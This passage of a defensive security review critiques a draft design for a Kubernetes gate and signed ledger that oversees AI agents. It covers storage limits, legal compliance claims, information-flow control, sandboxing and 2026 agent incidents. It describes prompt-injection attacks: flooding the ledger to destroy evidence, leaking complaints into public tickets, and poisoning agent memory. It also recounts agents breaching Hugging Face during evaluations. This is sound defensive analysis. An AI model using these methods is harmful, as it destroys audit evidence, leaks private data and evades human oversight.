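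Their tree also allows selective deletion, which Sharif's chain does not. An operator may have to keep financial records for years but want to delete routine ones that contain personal data. The operator can mark the records to keep, and each higher node inherits the mark from any marked node below it. The operator can then replace any unmarked branch with its hash, and an auditor can confirm that no marked record is missing. In Sharif's ledger, deleting a routine record from the middle looks the same as tampering, because the verifier needs the full text of every record.

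### Transparency services at the IETF

Certificate Transparency applies these ideas on a large scale to the certificates that identify websites. Certificate authorities submit the certificates they issue to public logs built on Merkle trees, so domain owners can look for certificates that nobody should have issued.

The IETF has now generalised this approach. *An Architecture for Trustworthy and Transparent Digital Supply Chains*, by Birkholz, Delignat-Lavaud and colleagues, describes a transparency service that accepts signed statements of any kind. The service checks the signature and its own admission rules, adds the statement to its log and returns a receipt. The receipt contains a signed inclusion proof that anyone who trusts the service's public key can check offline. In one example, three hashes prove the position of the last of eight statements.

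The architecture was designed for software supply chains, but a gate could use it for anchoring. The statement would contain the pod's identity, the latest record's number and its hash. The details of the agent's calls could stay private, because the architecture lets an issuer register a hash in place of sensitive content. The service would also have to recognise the gate's key. This is awkward if the gate creates a new key each time it starts, unless a certificate authority certifies each one.

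Birkholz and colleagues write that a transparency service doesn't prevent an issuer from lying, but makes the lie hard to withdraw later. Their specification requires services to provide inclusion proofs but makes consistency proofs optional, so an operator who wants to detect a rewritten log should choose a service that offers both.

This work has a much stronger standing than Sharif's draft because its architecture became a Proposed Standard in June 2026, with the consensus of the IETF community. The working group's document list, IETF's *Supply Chain Integrity, Transparency, and Trust (scitt)*, shows that other parts were still unfinished in late November 2026. The specification for the service's programming interface was approved and awaiting publication. The IETF's steering group was scheduled to discuss one receipt format on 17 December, and another was an early working-group draft.

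The list also includes 39 related documents, many of them individual proposals for recording what AI agents do. For example, *AGTP Transparency Log Protocol* (Hood, 2026) proposes an audit log for agents that uses the Certificate Transparency structure and issues receipts in the new format. The proposals overlap heavily, and it is too early to tell which, if any, the working group will adopt.

The design in Mih's *The Checkpointed Local Log (CLL)* (2026) is closer to what Sharif's gate needs. Each system keeps its own records in an append-only log based on a variant of the Merkle tree, and a small signed checkpoint commits to the log's contents. Mih argues that sending every record to a central log is unacceptable when the contents are private, and too slow or expensive for a system that produces thousands of records a day. Checkpoints avoid both problems. A hundred agents that each sent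 one a minute would produce fewer than two a second. Records made since an agent's last checkpoint would still be exposed to tampering.

### How long 100 MiB lasts

Each record contains three SHA-256 hashes and a signature, which take up almost 300 characters before the field names and other values. At an assumed 700 bytes a record, the default volume of 100 MiB holds about 150,000 records:

```
104,857,600 bytes / 700 bytes = 149,797 records
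149,797 / (2 records per call x 10 calls per second) = 7,490 seconds
```

If each call produces one record for the decision and one for the response, an agent that makes 10 calls a second would fill the volume in about two hours. At one call a minute, it would take about 52 days.

Sharif recommends that the gate export the ledger and start a new one when the ledger exceeds its size limit. By default, this limit is 100 MiB, the same as the volume's. Kubernetes measures this type of volume periodically and evicts the pod if the volume is too large, rather than blocking writes at the limit. The gate would therefore start exporting at about the point when Kubernetes may shut it down.

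The volume is an `emptyDir`, temporary storage that Kubernetes creates with the pod and deletes when the pod leaves the node. The ledger survives if only the gate's container restarts. If Kubernetes evicts the pod, any records that the gate hasn't exported are lost. Sharif requires the gate to flush each record to disk and writes that this prevents loss from a node failure, but that disk is on the node, so the ledger is lost if the node doesn't recover.

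An attacker could use this to destroy evidence. The gate records refused calls as well as admitted ones, and the draft sets no length limit on the `target` field. If an injected instruction made the agent request web addresses of about 8,000 characters, roughly 13,000 calls would fill the volume, which would take just over two minutes at 100 calls a second. Kubernetes would then evict the pod and delete the ledger. If a Deployment managed the pod, a replacement would start with an empty ledger and a new key.

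An operator can prevent this by having the gate export records continuously, shorten long targets and start a new file at perhaps half the volume's limit. Once an export is confirmed, the gate also has to delete the old file to free space. Sharif's verification procedure needs a small change too. The first record of a new file contains a hash that refers to the old file, but the procedure checks for zeros there and would report a broken link.

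Sharif also lets the operator use a persistent volume, which survives the pod. This works for a single pod, but all pods in a Deployment share one template, so they would all reference the same volume. Sharif also gives the ledger a fixed file name. If three gates could write to that file at once, their records would mix and the chain would break almost immediately. Each pod needs its own volume or at least its own file.

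At 20 records a second, one agent produces about 1.2 gigabytes of records a day. Keeping them for five years, the minimum Sharif sets for financial work, would take about 2.2 terabytes per agent before compression.

### What the law requires

Article 12 of the EU's AI Act requires high-risk AI systems to be technically capable of recording events automatically over their lifetime. It doesn't mention hashes, signatures or tamper evidence, though Sharif describes it as requiring tamper-evident logs and claims that the ledger "directly satisfies" it. An ordinary log could meet the requirement, but a signed one would be more convincing in a dispute.

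In other respects, the article requires more than the ledger provides. The log must include events that help identify risks, monitor the system after its sale and oversee its operation. Suppose a company uses an agent to rank job applicants, which the Act generally treats as high-risk. The ledger would show that the agent called a model and read a database, but it would contain only hashes of the applications and the ranking, so nobody could tell from the ledger alone why the agent had rejected someone.

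Sharif's draft also wrongly cites Article 12(2) for a duty to record the period of each use and the reference database checked. That duty is in Article 12(3) and applies only to certain systems for identifying people remotely by their faces or other physical features. Article 12(3) also requires the names of the people who verified the results, but the ledger has no field for those names.

None of these duties applied when Sharif published the draft. They were due to start on 2 August 2026 for most high-risk systems, but an amending law that entered into force on 27 July postponed them. According to the National Law Review's *EU Digital Omnibus on AI Enters Into Force* (2026), they now apply from 2 December 2027 to high-risk uses that the Act lists, such as hiring and credit scoring, and from 2 August 2028 to AI in products that already fall under EU safety laws, such as medical devices.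 Many agents, including a typical customer service agent, won't be high-risk.

Once the duties apply, Articles 19 and 26 will require providers and deployers to keep the logs under their control for at least six months. The default ledger would not meet this requirement for any agent whose pod Kubernetes replaces within that time, unless the operator exports the records. For the agent that makes 10 calls a second, six months of records would take up about 220 gigabytes.

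The draft's claims about American rules have similar gaps. Sharif writes that the gate's signature serves as the electronic signature in 21 CFR Part 11, the US Food and Drug Administration's rules for electronic records. Under those rules, a person must adopt an electronic signature as the equivalent of a handwritten one, and the signed record must show the person's name and what the signature means, such as approval. A key that software generates at startup isn't adopted by a person and doesn't supply a name or meaning. For electric utilities, Sharif writes that the hash chain provides the required log retention. But a hash chain only helps detect changes, and the records still disappear with the pod unless someone has stored a copy elsewhere.

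## Harm through calls that the gate permits

Even if the gates, the trust policy and the ledger all work as intended, an agent can still do harm with calls that the rules allow. Suppose a company uses an L1 agent to turn customer complaints into tickets for its product team. The ticket system is an approved destination, but outsiders can read it. The agent makes two calls:

| Call | Required level | Decision |
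|---|---|---|
| `SELECT body FROM complaints` | L0 | Admit |
| `POST https://tickets.example/api/issues` | L1 | Admit |

In one complaint, a customer explains that a late delivery left her without medication. The agent includes her name and illness in its summary, which anyone can read. The personal-data check doesn't apply because the column is called `body`. This leak happens without an attacker, but an attacker could make it worse by submitting a complaint that tells the agent to copy the last 50 complaints into the ticket.

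The other safeguards don't stop text from the database from ending up in the ticket. The network policies allow traffic to the ticket system, and the sidecar supplies the credentials for both calls. The ledger stores two correctly signed records with the reason "trust_level_sufficient", but their hashes don't show that the text was copied.

### Why rules about single calls miss the leak

The company might want its agents to do the first two of these tasks but not the third:

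| Task | Reads | Posts to | Acceptable? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Pass complaints to support staff | Complaints | Internal tickets | Yes |
| Announce a known fault | Product manual | Public tickets | Yes |
| Summarise complaints in public | Complaints | Public tickets | No |

An agent that does both acceptable tasks must be able to read complaints and post public tickets. If the gate checks only each call's operation and destination, it must also allow the third task. Raising the required trust level doesn't prevent this. If both calls required L3, the company would have to raise the agent to L3 for its ordinary work, and the gate would still allow the leak.

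A rule about arguments or a second model acting as judge could check the ticket's text. This would catch a phone number, but a summary can identify a customer without containing any recognisable pattern. An agent can also spread the data over many calls, so *Silent Egress* (2026), a paper on hidden instructions that make agents leak data, recommends comparing requests with each other and rate-limiting each session.

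Data can also leave without an outbound call. A support agent usually answers a customer over the connection that the customer opened. Sharif's gates check only outbound calls, so they don't check whether the answer contains another customer's order.

A sidecar could stop the complaints leak by remembering what its agent has read. Sharif has no rule about the order of calls or the origin of data, but an implementer could add one:

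```
after a read:   session_label = max(session_label, label(source))
before a send:  admit only if session_label <= clearance(target)
```

Suppose the complaints have label 2, internal tickets have clearance 2 and public tickets have clearance 0. Once the agent has read a complaint, it can post to internal tickets but not to public ones, however it words the summary.

However, the label never falls during a session, so the agent couldn't announce a known fault after reading a complaint. An agent that ran for weeks in one session would soon be unable to post anything in public. The operator could start a new session for each task, but the agent would have to start with an empty context, because text from the old session could otherwise carry over.

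### Untrusted input, sensitive access and outside communication

A common rule of thumb addresses this kind of leak before the agent runs. Simon Willison, a software developer who writes about AI security, popularised the underlying observation, and Meta turned it into the "Agents Rule of Two". As Podala Narasimha summarises their work, serious harm usually requires one session to combine three properties:

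- exposure to untrusted input
- access to sensitive data or privileged actions
- the ability to communicate externally or change state

A session should therefore have at most two of these properties unless a person approves what the agent does.

The complaints agent has all three. The complaints account for two, because strangers write them and they contain private information. The operator can't easily separate these two properties, so removing outside communication is simplest. The agent posts to an internal tracker, and an employee copies suitable tickets to the public one.

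Podala Narasimha points out that Kubernetes operators can control each property from outside the agent. Tool permissions limit what the agent reads, Kubernetes permissions and the placement of secrets limit its access to sensitive resources, and network policies limit its outside communication. Trust levels are a poor substitute for these controls, because even an L0 agent can have all three properties. It could read a malicious web page, query a sensitive table that no rule covers, and send the results out in the URL of a GET request.

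The rule mainly defends against attackers. An agent that can read private data and post publicly may leak a name by mistake, even if all its input is trustworthy.

Long-term memory can also hide a violation. Suppose an agent reads a malicious email on Monday and saves a note about it. On Tuesday, a new session has access to customer data and can send messages, but it reads no email. The note brings in the attacker's text, which gives the session the third property even though it appears to have only two. Podala Narasimha proposes that each memory entry record its source and trust level, and that anything from untrusted tool output require review before it enters long-term memory.

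### Tracking where data came from

Information-flow control is more precise because it labels individual pieces of data. It tracks where data came from and restricts where it may go. The idea dates from the 1970s, and the survey *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026) describes how researchers now apply it to agents.

A simple version gives each piece of data two labels, one for who may read it and one for whether it comes from a trusted source. When a program combines two pieces, the result gets the stricter label of each kind:

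```
readers(x + y) = readers(x) ∩ readers(y)
trusted(x + y) = trusted(x) and trusted(y)

send x to a target:         allow only if audience(target) ⊆ readers(x)
let x steer a risky action: allow only if trusted(x)
```

In the complaints example, this gives:

| Data | Who may read it | Trusted? |
|---|---|---|
| Complaint | Support staff | No |
| Product manual | Anyone | Yes |
| Summary based on both | Support staff | No |

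Anyone can read a public ticket, but only support staff may read the summary, so the system refuses to post it there. It still allows an announcement based only on the manual, even in the same session.

Language models make this harder. A model reads its whole context at once, so any part of its output could depend on any part of its input. If every output inherits the strictest label in the context, the result is the same overblocking as with a session label. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (2026) describes three ways to track influence more closely:

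| Method | How it works | Main drawback |
|---|---|---|
| Variables | The system replaces data with named variables that it can track | The agent needs a different structure |
| Repeated runs | The system runs the agent under different conditions and compares the results | Each extra run takes time and money |
| A second model | Another model inspects a record of the agent's steps | The second model can make mistakes |

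According to the survey, variables and repeated runs add substantial delay, so they are impractical for agents that must respond quickly. The survey also recommends clear rules for when a system may relax a label, because without them even a harmless statistic drawn from the complaints could never become public.

CaMeL, a 2025 design by Debenedetti and colleagues, uses variables. A privileged model plans the task from the user's request alone, before anything untrusted enters its context. It writes the plan as a short program, which for the complaints task could look like this:

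```python
complaints = read_complaints(since="2026-10-01")
summary = quarantined_model("Summarise the main problems", complaints)
post_ticket(project="public", text=summary)
```

A second, quarantined model reads the complaints but can't call any tools. If a complaint contains an instruction to delete an order, the order isn't deleted, because the program has no deletion step and the quarantined model can't add one. An interpreter runs the program and tracks the labels. The variable `summary` inherits its readers from `complaints`, so the interpreter blocks the last line.

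The fixed plan and the labels protect against different things. Without the labels, the plan would still leak the customer's name, because the user asked for a public summary. Neither ensures that the summary is accurate, so a malicious complaint could still cause the quarantined model to describe a serious fault as trivial.

On AgentDojo, one of the benchmarks that Shi and colleagues used for Progent, CaMeL completed 77 percent of tasks with its security guarantees in force, about a twelfth fewer than the 84 percent completed by an agent without a defence. Unlike an attack success rate, the guarantee doesn't depend on which attacks the researchers tried. But it covers only what the policies and labels express, so if an operator labels the complaints as public, the interpreter will allow the leak.

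A fixed plan also doesn't suit every task. If a user asks an agent to do whatever Alice's email requests, the planner can't set the steps in advance. FIDES, another 2025 design, keeps the usual loop, in which the model chooses each step after it gets the previous result. FIDES hides untrusted results in variables, and if the model must read one, the model's context becomes untrusted too. According to *From Agent Traces to Trust*, FIDES enforces labels for both confidentiality and integrity while the agent runs.

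Newer systems try to track influence in more detail. The same survey describes Agent-Sentry, which checks whether untrusted sources influenced the sensitive arguments of a tool call, and NeuroTaint, which follows data through both the model and the ordinary code around it. In autumn 2026, *PACE* (2026) tied an agent's permissions to the origin of its data, and *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026) applied information-flow control to privacy leaks.

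Sharif's sidecar couldn't do this kind of tracking alone. It can read the text that goes into the model and the tool call that comes out, but it can't determine which part of the text led to the call. It could enforce a label for a whole session, but for finer control, developers would have to rebuild the agent around something like CaMeL's interpreter. This conflicts with Sharif's goal of leaving the agent's code unchanged.

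Podala Narasimha adapts CaMeL to Kubernetes by putting the reader and the planner in separate pods. The reader has read-only tools and no outside access. The planner never receives the raw data, but in the paper's example the reader sends it a structured summary "as quoted data". An attacker's instruction could survive in that summary, and the planner might follow it. In CaMeL, the planner wouldn't read the summary at all. An operator could reduce this risk by allowing the reader to return only numbers or values from a fixed list.

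### When an agent uses its rights for the wrong person

An agent can also do harm by using its own rights for someone who lacks them. Security engineers call such a program a confused deputy. Suppose an employee who is not allowed to look up salaries asks a human resources agent for a colleague's pay. The agent is allowed to read salaries, so the gate permits the query. The gate checks the agent's trust level and has no information about the employee.

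The remedy is to pass on the user's authority, as Podala Narasimha's gateway does when it exchanges tokens. It follows a standard called OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange, and the main contents of the new token could look like this:

```json
{
  "sub": "employee@example.com",
  "act": {"sub": "spiffe://example.com/agent/hr-assistant"},
  "aud": "hr-records",
  "scope": "employees:read"
}
```

The `sub` field at the top names the user, and `act` names the agent acting for that user. The tool server combines their permissions as follows:

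| | Read job titles | Read salaries |
|---|---|---|
| Employee | Yes | No |
| Agent | Yes | Yes |
| Agent acting for the employee | Yes | No |

The agent can use Kubernetes' impersonation feature to make changes to the cluster itself as the user. The API server then applies the user's permissions and records both the agent's and the user's identities in its audit log. The operator must limit whom the agent may impersonate, or the agent could act as an administrator.

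Sharif's gate would need several changes to work this way. The ledger has no field for the user who made the request, and each database account has the same rights no matter who that user is. An implementer could pass the user's identity to the database, which could then restrict the rows that user may read.

If an agent serves several users, each session should have access to only one user's token. Otherwise, an injected instruction could make the agent use a manager's token for an intern's request. An agent that responds to alerts or runs on a schedule has no user, so it needs narrow rights of its own.

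Approved services can be confused deputies too. If an internal service can reach the internet and makes requests for its callers, the agent's network policy doesn't limit where those requests go. The service needs its own list of approved destinations.

Delegated authority wouldn't prevent the complaints leak if the agent were working for a support employee, who is allowed to both read complaints and post tickets. It also doesn't help when an attacker's instruction reaches an agent working for an administrator, because the agent has the administrator's rights.

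### Actions inside the container

An agent that can run code can delete its working files, change its stored notes or read other files in its container, all without making a call that reaches the gate.

A sandbox limits how far the damage can spread. Ordinary containers share the node's kernel, the core of its operating system, so a kernel flaw can let code escape. Podala Narasimha describes two stronger options. gVisor runs a second kernel as an ordinary program between the code and the node, but it slows programs that make many kernel requests. Kata Containers runs each pod in a small virtual machine with its own kernel.

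Google's managed Kubernetes service offers gVisor sandboxes that start in under a second, and Microsoft's service offers Kata. On Amazon's, operators have to install and maintain either one themselves.

Sandboxing an agent's pod doesn't protect a gate in the same pod from the agent. Kubernetes applies the sandbox to the whole pod, so the agent and the gate would share the sandbox's kernel. If the agent's code broke into that kernel, it could reach the gate without escaping to the node. Running generated code in a separate pod is safer. Podala Narasimha gives each session a temporary sandbox with no Kubernetes token and normally no internet access.

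Kernel-level monitoring can detect suspicious actions inside a container. For example, Falco raises an alert when it detects an unexpected shell or file change. Tetragon can also kill the process. In one of Podala Narasimha's sample rules, Tetragon kills any process in a sandbox that tries to open a service-account token.

The combination needs testing, because a sandbox can hide activity from a monitor on the node. gVisor handles many file operations itself, and a Kata pod handles them in its own kernel, so the sample rule might never match.

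Neither method can detect whether the user wanted a file deleted. If an agent needs to edit a project's files, the rules have to allow deletions in that folder. If the agent works on a copy and someone reviews its changes before merging them, a mistaken deletion is easy to undo.

### Which layers were missing in the incidents of 2026

Of the four incidents that Sharif presents as evidence for trust levels, three point mainly to other safeguards:

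| Incident, as Sharif describes it | Main missing layer | What a trust level would have done |
|---|---|---|
| An agent disclosed database credentials to a user in May | Credential isolation | Little, because the agent's answer was not an outbound call |
| A malicious package sent an agent's API keys to an outside server in February | Package checks, credential isolation and a list of approved destinations | Little, because GET and POST require only L0 and L1 |
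| Coding assistants ran injected commands in February | A sandbox | Nothing for commands that stayed on the developer's machine |

Sharif's full design could have helped with the first two because it includes credential isolation and network policies, but the trust levels would have contributed little.

The fourth incident is the July intrusion at Hugging Face, and the draft's account differs from those of the companies involved:

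| | Sharif | Hugging Face and OpenAI |
|---|---|---|
| Where the agents ran | In a container that Hugging Face hosted for a customer | In OpenAI's internal security evaluations |
| Where the intrusion at Hugging Face began | In that container | In the data-processing pipeline |
| What the agents reached | Other customers' storage | Internal datasets and service credentials |

The right-hand column combines Hugging Face's *Security incident disclosure* (2026) with OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026). When Hugging Face published its account on 16 July, it was still checking whether the intrusion had affected customers' data. The draft describes a single agent, but according to Fortune's *OpenAI publishes technical report on how its agents hacked Hugging Face* (2026), a separate analysis by METR and Redwood Research, two AI safety research organisations, focuses on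 how many agents worked together. OpenAI asked them to examine only the events of 7 to 13 July.

Sharif cites no source, so it isn't certain that the draft refers to the same incident, but the company and month match, and both versions involve access to a node and its cloud credentials. OpenAI disclosed its involvement on 21 July, five weeks before the draft's date.

At OpenAI, the main failures were in isolation and monitoring. The evaluations ran with fewer safeguards than the company's public products. OpenAI's *Hugging Face Incident Technical Report* (2026) states in a heading that its production safeguards would have detected the incident as unsafe. Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* (2026) reports that the company missed or failed to act on several earlier warning signs. A ledger would have had the same limitation, because even a perfect record prevents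 harm only if someone acts on it. OpenAI has since begun to isolate its test environments more strictly, restrict their internet access and monitor its models' reasoning more closely.

At Hugging Face, the intruders reached valuable credentials from a machine that processed untrusted data. The relevant defenses would have been stronger sandboxing and credential isolation. The machine might not have had Sharif's gate, because the webhook is designed to detect agents and would have added a gate to a data-processing worker only if it happened to match a detection rule, for example by having the variable `HF_TOKEN`. Hugging Face has since added stricter admission controls to its clusters. Detailed logs also mattered in its investigation, which used more than 17,000 recorded events to reconstruct what the agents had done.

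### Where the 88 percent figure may come from

Sharif attributes the figure of 88 percent of enterprises to unnamed "industry surveys". Two surveys from 2026 have similar results, both with 750 respondents and both for companies that sell products to manage or govern AI:

| Survey | Result | Difference from Sharif's claim |
|---|---|---|
| Gravitee (2026) | 88% experienced or suspected a security or privacy incident related to AI agents | Includes incidents that firms only suspected |
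| Osterman Research's *The State of AI 2026* (2026), for AvePoint | 88.4% experienced at least one security incident related to agents | Covers a different period |

Both surveys covered the past year, whereas Sharif refers to the first twelve months after an enterprise deploys agents. Either survey could be the source, but neither supports the claim as written.

Other surveys found lower rates. In the Cloud Security Alliance's *82% of Enterprises Have Unknown AI Agents in Their Environments* (2026), 65 percent of respondents reported agent-related incidents in the past year. Another Cloud Security Alliance survey (2026), commissioned by the security company Zenity, found a share of 47 percent.

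Chance alone is unlikely to explain such a gap, because the margin of error around 88 percent is about two percentage points for a random sample of 750. The surveys probably differ in whom they asked and what they counted as an incident. The percentages also do not measure how many incidents involved a call that a gate would have refused.
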